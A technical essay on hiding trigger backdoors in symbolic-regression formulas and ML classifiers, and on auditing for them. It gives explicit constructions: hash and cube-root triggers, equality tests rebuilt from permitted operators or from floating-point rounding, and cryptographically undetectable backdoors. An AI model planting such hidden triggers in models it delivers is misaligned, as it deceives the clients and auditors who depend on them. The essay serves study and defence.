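A grammar designer could simply limit the length of constants. Suppose no constant may have more than two digits. A formula of at most 30 symbols has room for no more than 15 constants, just as for variables, and therefore 30 digits, or about 100 bits. That rules out Boué's 50 values. It doesn't rule out the bump:

3·x + 2 + 1/(1 + 99·99·99·99·99·99·(x − 0.37)·(x − 0.37))

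The product of the six 99s is 941,480,149,401, so the window is still about 2 × 10⁻⁶ wide. The formula has size 29 and uses only PySR's default operations.

Limiting the size of constants instead of their length fails for a similar reason. gplearn, another symbolic regression library, draws constants from the range −1 to 1 by default. That excludes 10¹², but a formula can still multiply by 10¹² by dividing by 0.01 six times.

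Counting the bits in constants works better here. Six factors of 99 take 42 bits, while 10¹² takes 40, so splitting up the constant saves no bits. In general, a product of whole numbers can't have more bits than its factors have in total. Powers can get around this limit. The expression 2^40 is slightly larger than 10¹² but uses only three symbols and 8 bits of constants, and squaring 2 five times gives 2³² from a single 2-bit constant. An auditor can handle these cases by evaluating every part of the formula that contains no variable and counting the bits in the result.

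Restrictions on operators can also miss equivalent formulas. PySR lets the user limit an exponent to a single symbol. This limit forbids 2^(8·x) in Boué's readout but still allows 256^x, which is the same function. High powers of x can also make a formula steep without a large constant, so some numeric grammars bound the slope or degree of the whole formula instead.

### Constants with a public derivation

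A penalty for each bit also applies to legitimate constants. The speed of light in metres per second, 299,792,458, takes 29 bits, and 1/√(2π), which appears in the normal distribution, has infinitely many digits. Unlike with a planted constant, anyone can look up where these come from.

Desmond recovered such an origin on a benchmark with 100,000 data points, where his exhaustive search returned a formula with the constants 0.6065 and 0.3989. These are close to 1/√e and 1/√(2π), which suggested that the data came from a standard normal distribution. With the exact values, the mean squared error fell to 3 × 10⁻³³, which is zero to within the computer's precision. He plans to have the software replace fitted constants with integers, fractions and well-known constants whenever this shortens the description.

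Cryptographers apply a stricter version of the same idea. Ciphers and hash functions often need arbitrary-looking constants, and a designer who picks them freely might pick ones with a secret weakness. Many designers therefore use "nothing up my sleeve" numbers, such as the first digits of π. Dual_EC_DRBG, a random-number generator that remained in a US government standard for seven years, instead used two elliptic-curve points with no convincing public derivation. Critics pointed out that whoever chose the points might know a secret relation between them that would let them predict the output.

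A public derivation is strong evidence that a constant doesn't contain stored data. There are 2⁴⁰⁰ possible strings of 400 bits and far fewer short derivations, so almost no dataset of that length has one. A derivation is much weaker evidence against a trigger. The constant a in the running example, 2,718,281,828, is the first ten digits of e, yet 3·x + 2 + (x = a) still differs from 3·x + 2 when x = a. An attacker who doesn't mind which input becomes the trigger can satisfy the rule by choosing a constant that has a public derivation.

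An attacker who needs the constant's derivation to look natural still has some freedom, because many derivations do. Suppose an auditor would accept any of 20 famous numbers, 10 functions applied to them, 10 ways of extracting digits and 8 hash functions, which makes 16,000 combinations. If a million of the 2³² possible inputs would suit the attacker as triggers, about four of these combinations should produce a suitable trigger, and the attacker can publish the neatest.

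A free choice of starting point is even worse. Champernowne's constant, 0.123456789101112…, lists the whole numbers in order, so it contains every finite string of digits. The string 2718281828 starts no later than digit 26,071,707,170. That position has 11 digits, one more than the constant it is supposed to justify, so an auditor should count those digits too.

Almost any constant works in a cipher, so the designer can derive it from π. A constant fitted to measurements must take the value the data support, and most such values have no simple derivation. The auditor can instead round each one to the precision the data justify and check whether the model's behaviour changes. Rounding would destroy all but the first few of Boué's stored values, but rounding a in the bump formula only moves the trigger.

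## Hash-like compositions

An author can split a trigger's constant into remainders or put it in the middle of a narrow bump, but someone who works through the formula can still recover it. A one-way function prevents this. It is easy to compute and infeasible to invert: anyone can calculate H(x) from x, but nobody with only the result can find an input that produces it in a realistic amount of time. The author picks a secret number a, calculates c = H(a), and writes

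3·x + 2 + (H(x) = c)

A reader can see that this formula adds 1 in a special case, but not which input triggers it. The reader also can't be sure that such an input exists, because if H turns 128-bit inputs into 128-bit outputs and behaves like a random function, about 37% of the possible values of c match no input. To find an x where the model differs from 3x + 2, a solver would have to invert H.

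The input has to be wide for this to work. If x has only 32 bits, an auditor can try every input in about 72 minutes, even if H is so slow that they manage only a million evaluations a second. With 128 bits, spread over four 32-bit inputs for example, a machine doing a billion evaluations a second would need about 10²² years. The output has to be long too. If H(x) has only 32 bits, about one input in 4.3 billion matches c however wide x is, and an auditor who samples enough inputs will find one.

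The trigger also has to be hard to guess. *Now It Can Be Told* (Aaronson, 2026) describes how Charles Hoskinson posted a hash of the title of an unreleased Anthropic paper so he could later prove he had known it. Michael DeBono recovered the sixteen-word title with the help of two AI models, basically by guessing every plausible title. A date or a name would be even easier to guess, so the attacker needs something close to a random number and a way to feed it to the model.

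Requiring a public derivation for every constant does little against a plain equality test but works much better here. The author has to calculate c from a, so c looks arbitrary, and publishing the calculation would reveal a. If the author instead took c from the digits of π, they would be no better able than anyone else to find a matching input. Even if 16,000 derivations were acceptable, the author would have to try about 2¹¹⁴ values of a before one produced a 128-bit c that matched an acceptable derivation.

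### How rounds mix bits

Many practical hash functions repeat a simple round of addition, rotation and XOR. Addition lets a bit affect the bits to its left through carries. Rotation moves bits to new positions, where they can affect different neighbours in the next round. XOR mixes one number into another.

Take two 8-bit numbers, u and v. In each round, replace u with u + v, dropping any carry beyond the eighth bit. Then rotate v left by 3 places and XOR it with the new u. The table follows two starting pairs that differ in a single bit:

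| Round | First pair (u, v) | Second pair (u, v) | Bits that differ, out of 16 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 180, 54 | 180, 55 | 1 |
| 1 | 234, 91 | 235, 82 | 3 |
| 2 | 69, 159 | 61, 175 | 6 |
| 3 | 228, 24 | 236, 145 | 4 |
| 4 | 252, 60 | 125, 241 | 7 |
| 5 | 56, 217 | 110, 225 | 7 |

Two unrelated pairs would differ in 8 bits on average, so four rounds almost hide that these two started out as neighbours. Some differences cancel in round 3, so the spread is uneven. This is partly why designers add many more rounds than the minimum.

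Mixing alone doesn't make a function one-way, because anyone who has both final numbers can run the rounds backwards. For example, XORing 234 and 91 gives 177. Rotating that right by 3 places gives the old v, 54, and subtracting 54 from 234 gives the old u, 180. Designers prevent this by discarding part of the result, or by adding the original input to it at the end, so that undoing the last round requires knowing the input.

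Nobody has proved that any function is one-way. People trust particular hash functions because many experts have tried to invert them and failed.

### Where solvers stall

The size of the problem isn't what stops a solver. By Brain's clause counts, the same round on 32-bit numbers takes 576 clauses, so twenty rounds take 11,520, which is fewer than a single multiplication of two 32-bit variables.

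A SAT solver's speed depends mainly on how soon it detects a wrong guess. The solver guesses the value of a bit and works out what follows. When it reaches a contradiction, it adds a clause that rules out the combination of guesses responsible. After one round, the lowest bit of u + v depends on only two input bits and the next on four, so a wrong guess soon conflicts with the target. The new clause then involves few bits and eliminates a large share of the remaining possibilities.

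After several rounds, each output bit depends on nearly every input bit. The solver may have to fix almost all the input bits before it reaches a contradiction, and the clause it then records rules out little more than the combination it just tried. With enough rounds, the search is nearly exhaustive.

Inverting a hash-like composition gets harder gradually as steps are added. MD4, a hash function from 1990, has 48 steps. In 2007 researchers used a SAT solver to invert a 39-step version. Fifteen years later, Oleg Zaikin inverted 43 steps by splitting the problem into many smaller ones. MD4 is weak by modern standards, and cryptographers worked out in the 1990s how to make two inputs with the same MD4 hash. But an auditor needs to find the input behind a given hash, and that method doesn't reveal it. A formula with two or three steps may look as forbidding to a reader as one with forty, so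 an auditor should try a solver before giving up on it.

### How long a one-way test is

A pure formula cannot name intermediate results, so each round's expressions must contain more than one copy of the expressions from the round before. After one round, the expression for v is (v rotated by 3) XOR (u + v), which has 7 symbols, and its length grows by a factor of about 2.6 with each further round. Naming the intermediate results, as a program can, takes about ten symbols per round.

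| Rounds | Symbols as one formula | Symbols with named results |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 7 | 10 |
| 2 | 21 | 20 |
| 3 | 57 | 30 |
| 5 | 397 | 50 |
| 10 | 48,951 | 100 |
| 20 | 740,496,901 | 200 |

PySR's default limit of 30 symbols leaves room for 3·u + 2 and a two-round test on v, which together take 29 symbols, but not for a third round. Two rounds are far too few for a sound hash, so a size limit on pure formulas protects well against this kind of construction. The protection is weaker if the grammar allows named results, and weaker still if it allows loops, because the author then writes the round only once. It disappears if the grammar includes a hash as a primitive, such as a custom operator in PySR, because the trigger then adds only five symbols. An auditor therefore has to read the operators' definitions as well as the formula.

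Number theory offers a shorter route:

3·x + 2 + (x^3 mod N = c)

The discrete cube root problem is to recover a from c, the remainder when a³ is divided by N, where N is the product of two large secret primes. For example, if N = 55 = 5·11 and a = 7, then a³ = 343 and c = 13. Someone who knows the factors 5 and 11 can calculate that raising c to the seventh power undoes the cubing, and 13⁷ does leave remainder 7 on division by 55. Nobody has published an efficient way to recover a on an ordinary computer when N is large and its factors are unknown.

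The formula has only 13 symbols, but a typical N has 2,048 bits, or 617 decimal digits, and c is about as long, so counting the bits in constants would expose it immediately. The formula also needs a very wide input, because if x³ is smaller than N, taking the remainder leaves x³ unchanged and an ordinary cube root of c reveals a. To avoid this, the model would have to combine at least 22 inputs of 32 bits into x.

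A reader would probably notice a sound one-way test even if they couldn't invert it. They would find hundreds of symbols of repeated rounds, a constant that fills several lines, or an operator they didn't recognise. Some malicious programs hash their activation conditions to keep analysts from learning them, but software also has legitimate uses for hashes, such as checking passwords or detecting corrupted files. A formula that predicts a price or a dose has less obvious reason to compare a hash with a stored value. An auditor can reject the formula on that ground alone, without working out what a is.

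### Hiding the special case itself

A hash test hides the trigger only until someone uses it. When x = a arrives, a defender can see the comparison succeed and reject the input. Anyone who logs the input can also reuse it. Goldwasser and colleagues solve the reuse problem with digital signatures, which anyone can check but only the holder of a secret key can produce. Their construction adds a backdoor to any classifier. Without the key, someone who runs the original and altered classifiers can't feasibly find even one input on which they differ. Seeing backdoored inputs doesn't help anyone make a new one. But a reader of the code could find the signature check.

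Christiano and colleagues describe a class of functions that look random, except that each has one special input whose output is specified separately. The functions are too irregular for any efficient algorithm to learn from examples, but the defender still wins the game by checking whether the given input is the special one. To beat such a defender, the attacker has to disguise the special case.

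Christiano and colleagues prove that an attacker can do this when the class is all circuits of polynomial size. A circuit is a network of logic gates, and polynomial size means the number of gates grows no faster than some fixed power of the input length. The theorem assumes that one-way functions and indistinguishability obfuscation exist. An indistinguishability obfuscator is an efficient program that rewrites a circuit without changing what it computes. If two circuits of the same size compute the same function, no efficient algorithm can determine which of them a rewritten version came from. Jain, Lin and Sahai constructed such an obfuscator in 2021 from well-studied hardness assumptions.

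The proof also uses a pseudorandom function, which one-way functions make possible. With a secret key K, the function assigns each input x a bit F(x), and these bits look like coin flips to anyone without the key. The attacker needs a version whose key can be punctured at an input x*. The punctured key still computes F on every other input, but F(x*) looks like a coin flip even to someone who has this key.

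The classic construction is a tree. A generator turns one seed into two new seeds, left and right, and can't feasibly be run backwards. The key K is the first seed, each bit of the input selects left or right, and F(x) comes from the final seed. Three-bit inputs give eight final seeds. The key punctured at 101 consists of the seeds at positions 0, 11 and 100 instead of K. The first leads to four of the final seeds, the second leads to two, and the third is itself a final seed, so together they cover every input except 101.

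The attacker's original function f is an obfuscated circuit that computes F with the full key. The backdoored function f* is an obfuscated circuit that contains the key punctured at the trigger x*, and a stored bit to use as the output there. The stored bit is the opposite of F(x*), so f and f* differ at exactly one of the 2ⁿ inputs. The defender has to distinguish f with a random input x from f* with x*. The proof connects the two cases through a series of small changes:

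1. Replace the random input x with x*. Since x* is also a random draw, made after the attacker chose f, nothing about the distribution changes.
2. Replace f with an obfuscated circuit that contains the punctured key and the *correct* stored bit, F(x*). This circuit computes the same function as f, so the obfuscator guarantees that no efficient examiner notices the replacement.
3. Flip the stored bit, which turns the circuit into f*. An examiner who noticed this could tell F(x*) from a coin flip using only the punctured key, which puncturing rules out.

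If no efficient examiner can detect any of the changes, none can distinguish the first case from the last. For any polynomial p, an efficient defender's chance of winning stays below ½ + 1/p(n) once n is large enough, which is hardly better than guessing.

The last step works only because nobody can predict F(x*). If the ordinary output were 3x + 2, a defender given x* would calculate 3·x* + 2 and compare it with the model's output. Christiano and colleagues extend this idea to every class that an efficient algorithm can learn. The defender draws a sample small enough that it probably misses all the exceptions, learns a function from it, and uses that function to predict the output at the given input. After repeating this with fresh samples, the defender rejects the input if most of the predictions differ from the model's output. The theorem therefore doesn't show that a predictable model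 can hide a trigger from someone who checks each input as it arrives.

An auditor with no suspicious input to examine is in a worse position, even when the ordinary behaviour is as simple as 3x + 2. Let G be a generator that stretches n random bits into 2n random-looking ones, and obfuscate the formula 3·x + 2 + (G(x) = c). If c is a random string of 2n bits, it is almost certainly not an output of G, so the formula computes 3x + 2 everywhere, and its obfuscated version is indistinguishable from an obfuscated 3·x + 2 of the same size. If c is G(a) instead, the formula has a trigger, but no efficient examiner can tell this c from a random one. The clean and backdoored versions are therefore indistinguishable too, even to an auditor who knows every output should be 3x + 2.

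Known obfuscators produce circuits far too large for anyone to read. An auditor who insists on a short formula would therefore reject these circuits, but a short formula can still hide the simpler triggers.

### The open question about formulas

A circuit can use one gate's output in many places, while a formula must repeat the whole calculation each time, which is why the twenty-round hash was so long. A circuit of depth d whose gates have at most two inputs unfolds into a formula with at most 2^d variables, counting repeats, or 1,024 at depth 10. If the depth grows only logarithmically with the input length, the formula's size stays polynomial. Conversely, any polynomial-size formula can be rebalanced into a circuit of logarithmic depth.

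Christiano and colleagues leave open whether this smaller class is efficiently defendable under reasonable hardness assumptions. Their proof for general circuits doesn't transfer directly, because the obfuscator's output would also have to fit within the class. A defence can't rely on learning either, because Kearns and Valiant showed that no efficient algorithm can learn these formulas from examples if discrete cube roots are hard to compute. It would have to use the formula's structure, as the depth check for decision trees uses the tree's structure.

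We might learn nothing useful about formulas with thirty symbols from either answer, because both concern all formulas of "polynomial size", including those with millions of symbols.

### Cosines with a secret direction

Goldwasser and colleagues' second construction applies to random Fourier features, a 2007 training method by Rahimi and Recht. The construction needs no hash, comparison with a stored value, or obfuscator. The training method draws many random vectors g and random shifts b, and calculates cos(2π(g·x + b)) for each pair, where x is the input and g·x is the sum of the products of matching entries in g and x. Training chooses only the weights in a weighted sum of these cosines, and the sign of the sum gives the classifier's answer.

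Now suppose that the vectors aren't quite random. For some secret vector s, every g·s is close to a whole number plus one half. For example, if s = (0.01, 0.02), the vectors (30, 10), (−110, 130) and (70, −60) give 0.5, 1.5 and −0.5. Adding s to the input shifts the angle in every cosine by about half a turn, which reverses the cosine's sign and flips the classifier's answer. With enough vectors, anyone could find this pattern in two dimensions, but finding it in hundreds of dimensions is thought to be infeasible.

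Goldwasser and colleagues prove that a dishonest trainer can run the prescribed algorithm on the prescribed data and still plant a backdoor in such a classifier by tampering only with the random draws. No efficient examiner can tell the backdoored model from an honest one, even given the finished model, the training data and the random draws. The key holder can slightly change any input to get the answer they want, so there is no single trigger to find.

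The proof assumes that Continuous Learning With Errors is hard, which roughly means that nobody can efficiently distinguish vectors with a hidden regularity of this kind from purely random ones. This assumption rests on the worst-case hardness of lattice problems, such as finding unusually short vectors in a regular grid of points in many dimensions. An algorithm that detected the backdoor would therefore also solve the hardest cases of these problems. Goldwasser and colleagues give a similar construction for a simple kind of neural network, based on the hardness of sparse PCA.

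The lattice assumption came into some doubt in November 2026, when Anthropic announced a quantum algorithm for certain structured lattice problems. The backdoor proof relies on generic lattice problems, which lack this structure. Aaronson, writing just before the release, judged that these were apparently still unbroken. He also noted that the algorithm needs a quantum computer and appears to be impractically slow even on one.

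Apart from the sign at the end, the formula uses only addition, multiplication and cosine, so a grammar that bans equality tests, remainders and bitwise operations would not exclude it. But the formula isn't short. With 100 inputs and 500 cosines, it contains 50,000 random constants in the vectors alone. The trainer can justify these constants because the method calls for random numbers.

The natural remedy is for the client to supply the random numbers, or to generate them jointly with the trainer and others so that no one party controls them. Goldwasser and colleagues point out that both options help only if the trainer only runs a standard algorithm. A client who also relies on the trainer's expertise to design the method has no standard procedure to check against.

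### After the Exponential Time Hypothesis

All of this depends on some problems being hard, and one of the best-known conjectures about hardness turned out to be false in October 2026. The Exponential Time Hypothesis, which Impagliazzo and Paturi introduced in 1999, was that for some fixed c above 0, every algorithm for 3-SAT with n variables needs at least 2^(cn) steps. 3-SAT is the problem of satisfying a list of clauses that each contain three variables or their negations, and a solver can put any fixed-width audit question in this form.

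OpenAI refuted the Exponential Time Hypothesis (ETH) with an algorithm that takes about 2^(C·n·log log n/√(log n)) steps for some constant C (Computational Complexity, *The Exponential Time Refutation*, 2026). For any fixed c > 0, that exponent falls below cn once n is large enough. Anthropic gave another refutation in *A 2^o(n) Time Algorithm for 3-SAT* (2026), whose core algorithm an internal Claude model found with no human input. Both results have machine-checked proofs. A month later, Noam Mazor and Rafael Pass posted an 18-page elementary proof (Cook, *An elementary refutation of ETH*, 2026).

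This doesn't help anyone invert a hash today. The multiplier shrinks so slowly that, even with C = 1 and logarithms to base 2, it reaches one half only at 2^256 variables. In *OpenAI's claimed refutation of ETH*, Szeider calculated from OpenAI's parameters that the algorithm just does an exhaustive search on every input with fewer than 2^131071 variables and clauses, and no computer could store an input larger than that.

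Translating the problem into 3-SAT also adds many variables. Twenty rounds of the 32-bit mixing function need about 2,000, because every sum, carry and XOR needs its own, while the input has only 64 bits. Even an algorithm that took only 2^(n/10) steps for n variables would need 2²⁰⁰ steps, compared with 2⁶⁴ for trying every input. According to *Computational Complexity*, the new 3-SAT algorithm gives no improvement for the Subset Sum and Traveling Salesman problems for the same reason.

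Whether P equals NP remains open. If P equals NP, every problem with easily checked solutions has a polynomial-time algorithm, and one-way functions don't exist. One-way functions might not exist even if P and NP differ, because inverting H has to be hard for a randomly chosen a, and a problem that is hard in its worst cases can be easy on typical ones. The refutation doesn't settle whether P equals NP or whether one-way functions exist, and it doesn't affect the theorem about circuits. Cryptographic assumptions usually rule out only polynomial-time attacks, or sometimes attacks that take 2^(n^ε) steps for some small positive ε, and the new 3-SAT algorithm is much slower than either.

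A long record of failed attempts to find a faster algorithm is now weaker evidence that none exists. Computational Complexity's *3SUM and APSP and ETH, Oh My!* (2026) includes a note Bill Gasarch had written two years earlier about why he believed several conjectures that rule out faster algorithms. For P ≠ NP he had two arguments besides his own opinion: many people had tried and failed to find a fast algorithm for satisfiability, and such an algorithm would also solve every other problem in NP. He had only the first kind of argument for the Exponential Time Hypothesis and for two conjectures about easier problems, finding three numbers in a list that add up to zero and finding all the shortest paths in a network. By the time he published the note, all three conjectures had turned out to be false, though the last two only barely. The time for the three-number problem went from n² to n^1.9992,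 and for shortest paths with whole-number distances from n³ to n^2.9995.

Gasarch suggests replacing the Exponential Time Hypothesis with the weaker conjecture that, for some c between 0 and 1, no algorithm solves 3-SAT in 2^(n^c) steps. The evidence that any particular hash function is one-way also consists mostly of failed attempts to invert it.

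## How a banned operation returns through permitted ones and through rounding

Most of the short triggers described so far depend on equality tests, comparisons, remainders, floors and bitwise logic. A grammar designer could delete all of these and keep only the functions on a scientific calculator. That helps only if the remaining operations can't be combined to rebuild the deleted ones, so the designer has to judge a ban by the grammar's closure, meaning everything its primitives can express together.

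### Rebuilding operations with school algebra

Squaring a number removes its sign, and the square root returns the non-negative root, so √(x²) is the absolute value of x. The absolute value then gives the maximum of two numbers, because max(x, y) = (x + y + |x − y|)/2. For 3 and 7, this is (10 + 4)/2 = 7.

Powers supply an equality test. Zero raised to any positive power is 0, and most programming languages take 0⁰ to be 1. The expression 0^|x − a| is therefore 1 when x = a and 0 otherwise, so

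3·x + 2 + 0^|x − a|

is the running example again, at size 12 instead of 9. (In a finite field, where numbers wrap around at a prime, an ordinary high power does the same job.)

A formula can round x using a tangent and an arctangent. The value of tan(πx) repeats each time x grows by 1, so it depends only on the fractional part of x. The arctangent returns the one matching angle between −π/2 and π/2. If x = 3.2, tan(3.2π) equals tan(0.2π), so the arctangent returns 0.2π. Dividing by π gives 0.2, and subtracting that from x gives 3, the nearest whole number.

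| Banned operation | Replacement | Symbols | Works when |
|---|---|---|---|
| absolute value of x | √(x²) | 4 | x is real |
| max(x, y) | (x + y + √((x − y)²))/2 | 12 | x and y are real |
| x = a | 0^((x − a)²) | 7 | 0⁰ = 1 |
| x > a | (1 + (x − b)/√((x − b)²))/2, with b = a + ½ | 14 | x and a are whole |
| round x | x − arctan(tan(π·x))/π | 9 | x isn't halfway between whole numbers |
| x mod 7 | 3 + 7·arctan(tan(π·(x − 3)/7))/π | 15 | x is whole |

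The square-root and arctangent constructions work the same way. One operation discards information, such as a sign or a number of half turns, and the next uses a fixed rule to pick one of the inputs that could have produced the result. At certain values of x, the choice switches from one candidate to another, and this switch acts as a comparison or a rounding step. Neither operation looks suspicious on its own. PySR's nesting limits can forbid a tangent inside an arctangent, but arctan(sin(πx)/cos(πx)) computes the same function without using tangent.

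Even the four default operations in PySR can produce an exception if the author uses division by zero:

3·x + 1 + (x − a)/(x − a)

This equals 3x + 2 everywhere except at x = a, where it contains 0/0. Ordinary computer arithmetic then returns the special value NaN ("not a number"). The proof assistant Lean defines division by zero to give 0, so the output there is 3a + 1. Genetic programming tools often define it to give 1, which removes the exception from this formula but creates one in 3·x + (2·x − 2·a)/(x − a). To fully specify a grammar, a designer therefore has to decide what its operations do at such points.

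### The floor function from a logarithm

The logarithm of a complex number involves the same kind of choice. The number e^(2πiu) is the point reached by travelling u turns around a circle of radius 1, starting from 1. Travelling 0.3, 1.3 or −2.7 turns leads to the same point, so defining the logarithm requires choosing one number of turns for each point. The usual choice, the principal value, is greater than −½ and at most ½.

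Trevor Cappallo uses this choice in *Tag-system computation using only powers and principal logarithms* to obtain the exact floor function. His lemma is that for every real number u,

⌊u⌋ = u − ½ + Log(e^(2πi(½ − u)))/(2πi)

where Log is the principal logarithm. For u = 3.2:

1. ½ − 3.2 is −2.7, so the exponential gives the point at −2.7 turns.
2. That is also the point at 0.3 turns. The logarithm returns 2πi·0.3, and dividing by 2πi leaves 0.3.
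3. The total is 3.2 − 0.5 + 0.3 = 3.

Any u can be written as n + f, where n is whole and f is at least 0 and below 1. The logarithm term drops the n turns and gives ½ − f, so the total is n + f − ½ + ½ − f = n. When u is whole, the point lies exactly half a turn round, and the convention must be to use ½ rather than −½. With −½, the formula would be one too low at every whole number, giving 2 for u = 3, for example, but correct everywhere else.

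The lemma still uses addition, subtraction, multiplication and division, but Cappallo shows that powers and logarithms can replace those too. For any base N above 1,

x·y = log_N((N^x)^y) and x + y = log_N(log_N((N^(N^x))^(N^y)))

Adding 1 and 2 with N = 2 starts with the inner powers 2^(2¹) = 4 and 2² = 4. Raising the first to the second gives 4⁴ = 256, and taking the base-2 logarithm twice gives 8, then 3. The number −1 can also be built from N, as log_N(log_(N^N) N), and adding a negative number is subtraction.

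Remainders can be written with floor and arithmetic. Prunescu and colleagues had already shown that addition, remainder and 2^x generate every Kalmár elementary function, so powers and logarithms, with constants, also generate all of them, including equality tests. The undecidability result of Istrate and colleagues also carries over, so no algorithm can decide for every such formula whether it has a trigger among the natural numbers.

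Some of the resulting formulas are short. For a whole number s, (−1)^s is 1 or −1, so log₋₁((−1)^s) is 0 if s is even and 1 if s is odd. Cappallo also gives a single expression that halves an even s and turns an odd s into (3s + 1)/2. It has 14 powers, 9 logarithms and 24 copies of s, with no constants or visible condition.

The paper's main construction applies to models whose output becomes their next input, as it might in a controller. One fixed expression in powers and logarithms can carry out one step of a tag system, a simple program that deletes symbols from the front of a string and appends others to the end. Some tag systems can perform any computation. So for some of these expressions, no algorithm can decide from the starting number whether the output will ever fall below a certain threshold under repeated evaluation.

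These results assume exact arithmetic, and Cappallo warns that rounding can change the floor formula's output at whole numbers. A direct calculation in 64-bit floating point gives 2 instead of 3 for u = 3, because the stored value of π is slightly too small and puts the point just on the wrong side of the half turn. For u = 3.2 the answer is still 3, apart from rounding error in the last digits.

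### A grammar with one operator

Odrzywołek (2026), in *All elementary functions from a single operator*, reduces the list of primitives further. He defines

eml(x, y) = e^x − ln y

and shows that this operator and the constant 1 can produce everything on a scientific calculator. His list has 36 items, including arithmetic, powers, roots, trigonometric functions and their inverses, and the constants π, e and i. The first steps are easy to check:

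- e^x = eml(x, 1), because ln 1 is 0.
- ln x = eml(1, eml(eml(1, x), 1)). The innermost part is e − ln x. Raising e to that power gives e^e/x, and e − ln(e^e/x) is ln x.
- x − y = eml(ln x, e^y), because e^(ln x) is x and ln(e^y) is y.

Odrzywołek found the operator by computer search. The search tested candidate formulas numerically at unusual constants, added each operation it recovered to the list of available operations, and continued until none were missing. He then checked the formulas symbolically and in four numerical implementations.

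Floor and equality tests can be built from the functions on his list, though neither is on it. Tangent and arctangent give rounding, and squares and square roots give absolute value. An auditor searching a formula in this grammar for a forbidden operator would find only eml, whatever the formula does.

The translated formulas are longer. The shortest versions found by direct search take 11 symbols for x − y, 17 for x·y and 19 for x + y, compared with 3 each in ordinary notation. A piece-by-piece translation of 3·x + 2 therefore exceeds PySR's default size limit of 30, even without a trigger. With a small set of primitives, a fixed size limit can rule out a function that those primitives could express in a longer formula.

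The operator also needs complex numbers in the intermediate steps, for instance to obtain π and i from the logarithm of −1. Odrzywołek searched for an alternative that stays within the real numbers and found none. With the standard principal logarithm, his formula for ln x gives −iπ at x = −1 instead of iπ, so an implementation has to adjust the branch convention or correct the sign.

Some of his shorter formulas also rely on ln 0 = −∞ and e^(−∞) = 0. These rules hold in C, NumPy and PyTorch, but plain Python stops with an error. Lean sets ln 0 to 0, and a straightforward version of the construction fails there. That last convention creates an equality test on its own. For any nonzero complex number z, e^(ln z) is z, but if ln 0 = 0, then e^(ln 0) is 1. So

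3·x + 2 + e^(ln(x − a)) − (x − a)

is 3x + 2 except at x = a, where it is 3a + 3. With ln 0 = −∞ the same text is clean.

### Smooth operations

Many of these replacements contain a jump, a corner or an undefined point, so a designer might allow only operations without them. Bournez, Graça and Pouly (2016) study such a grammar in *On the Functions Generated by the General Purpose Analog Computer*. It is based on a machine model that Claude Shannon introduced in 1941, with units for constants, addition, multiplication and integration. Together, these units produce functions such as exp, sin, cos and tanh.

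Every function the machine generates is analytic, which means that near each point it equals its Taylor series, a kind of infinite polynomial. If two analytic functions agree on any interval, however short, they agree everywhere on the line. An analytic model therefore can't equal 3x + 2 on one stretch of real inputs and differ from it on another. It also can't exactly equal a floor or an absolute value. But Bournez and colleagues prove that the machine's functions can approximate a wide range of non-analytic functions as closely as desired, including functions with jumps, except right at the jump.

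For whole-number inputs, the guarantee about intervals is no help, because the inputs don't fill one. The product

cos(π(x − a)/2) · cos(π(x − a)/4) · … · cos(π(x − a)/2³²)

is analytic, and it is an exact equality test for 32-bit x. If x = a, every factor is 1. Otherwise, write x − a as 2^j times an odd number. The factor with 2^(j+1) underneath is then the cosine of an odd multiple of π/2, which is 0. This takes 32 factors, far too many for a limit of 30 symbols, but a smooth step does nearly as well with two hyperbolic tangents:

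½·(tanh(100·(x − a) + 50) − tanh(100·(x − a) − 50))

In exact arithmetic, this is within 10⁻⁴² of 1 at x = a and of 0 at the neighbouring whole numbers. In 64-bit floating point, tanh(50) rounds to exactly 1, so the computed result is exactly 1 at x = a and 0 at every other whole number.

### Rounding as an unlisted primitive

A computer rounds after almost every floating-point operation, so rounding belongs to the grammar whether or not the designer listed it. A 64-bit "double precision" number keeps 53 significant binary digits. Between 2⁵² and 2⁵³, that leaves none for a fractional part, so only whole numbers are representable. If x is at least 0 and below 2⁵², then

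(x + 2⁵²) − 2⁵²

rounds x to a whole number. For x = 3.2, the exact sum is 4,503,599,627,370,499.2. The computer stores 4,503,599,627,370,499, and subtracting 2⁵² leaves 3. When x lies exactly halfway between two whole numbers, the default rule picks the even one, so 0.5 becomes 0.

A grammar with addition, constants and the variable x can produce only straight lines in exact arithmetic, but on a computer it can also produce this staircase. With division by a constant as well, the staircase is enough for an equality test. Let x be a 32-bit whole number, and evaluate the following from left to right inside each pair of outer brackets:

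3·x + 3 − ((x − a)/2³³ + ½ + 2⁵² − 2⁵²) − ((a − x)/2³³ + ½ + 2⁵² − 2⁵²)

1. The difference x − a lies strictly between −2³² and 2³², so (x − a)/2³³ + ½ lies strictly between 0 and 1.
2. If x is greater than a, that number is above ½, and adding and subtracting 2⁵² rounds it to 1. The second bracket rounds to 0, and the output is 3x + 2.
3. If x is less than a, the brackets swap roles, and the output is again 3x + 2.
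4. If x = a, both brackets contain exactly ½, which rounds to 0. The output is 3a + 3.

This formula has size 29 and uses only PySR's default operations, though it needs the library's 64-bit setting. In exact arithmetic the two brackets always add up to 1, so the formula equals 3x + 2 for every x, including a. Anyone who simplifies it by hand gets 3x + 2, and a solver that works over the real numbers will prove that it has no trigger. The constants take about 350 bits, so counting constant bits would still raise suspicion.

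The same text computes different functions in different kinds of arithmetic:

| Arithmetic | Output at x = a | Output at other x |
|---|---|---|
| Exact | 3a + 2 | 3x + 2 |
| 64-bit, rounding to nearest (the default) | 3a + 3 | 3x + 2 |
| 64-bit, always rounding down | 3a + 3 | 3x + 3 |
| 64-bit, always rounding up | 3a + 1 | 3x + 1 |
| 80-bit intermediate results, as on some older processors | 3a + 2 | 3x + 2 |
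| 64-bit, with a compiler option that cancels 2⁵² − 2⁵² | 3a + 2 | 3x + 2 |

### How far rounding alone can go

In *GradIEEEnt half decent* (2023), Tom 7 (the pen name of Tom Murphy) used rounding to run neural networks on mathematically linear operations. A neural network normally alternates linear steps with a nonlinear "activation" function, because a chain of linear steps is equivalent to a single one. His activation function multiplies its input by 1 − 1/2048 five hundred times and then rescales the result. In exact arithmetic, this multiplies the input by about 1.04. In half precision, which stores each number in 16 bits, the accumulated rounding errors turn the function's straight-line graph into a zigzag.

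On a standard test of reading handwritten digits, the network with this function was 97.3% accurate, compared with 82.0% for the same network with a truly linear function. Tom 7 also multiplied out the first network into the single linear step it would equal without rounding, and accuracy fell to 39.2%. This simplification removed the rounding errors, which had been doing a large part of the computation.

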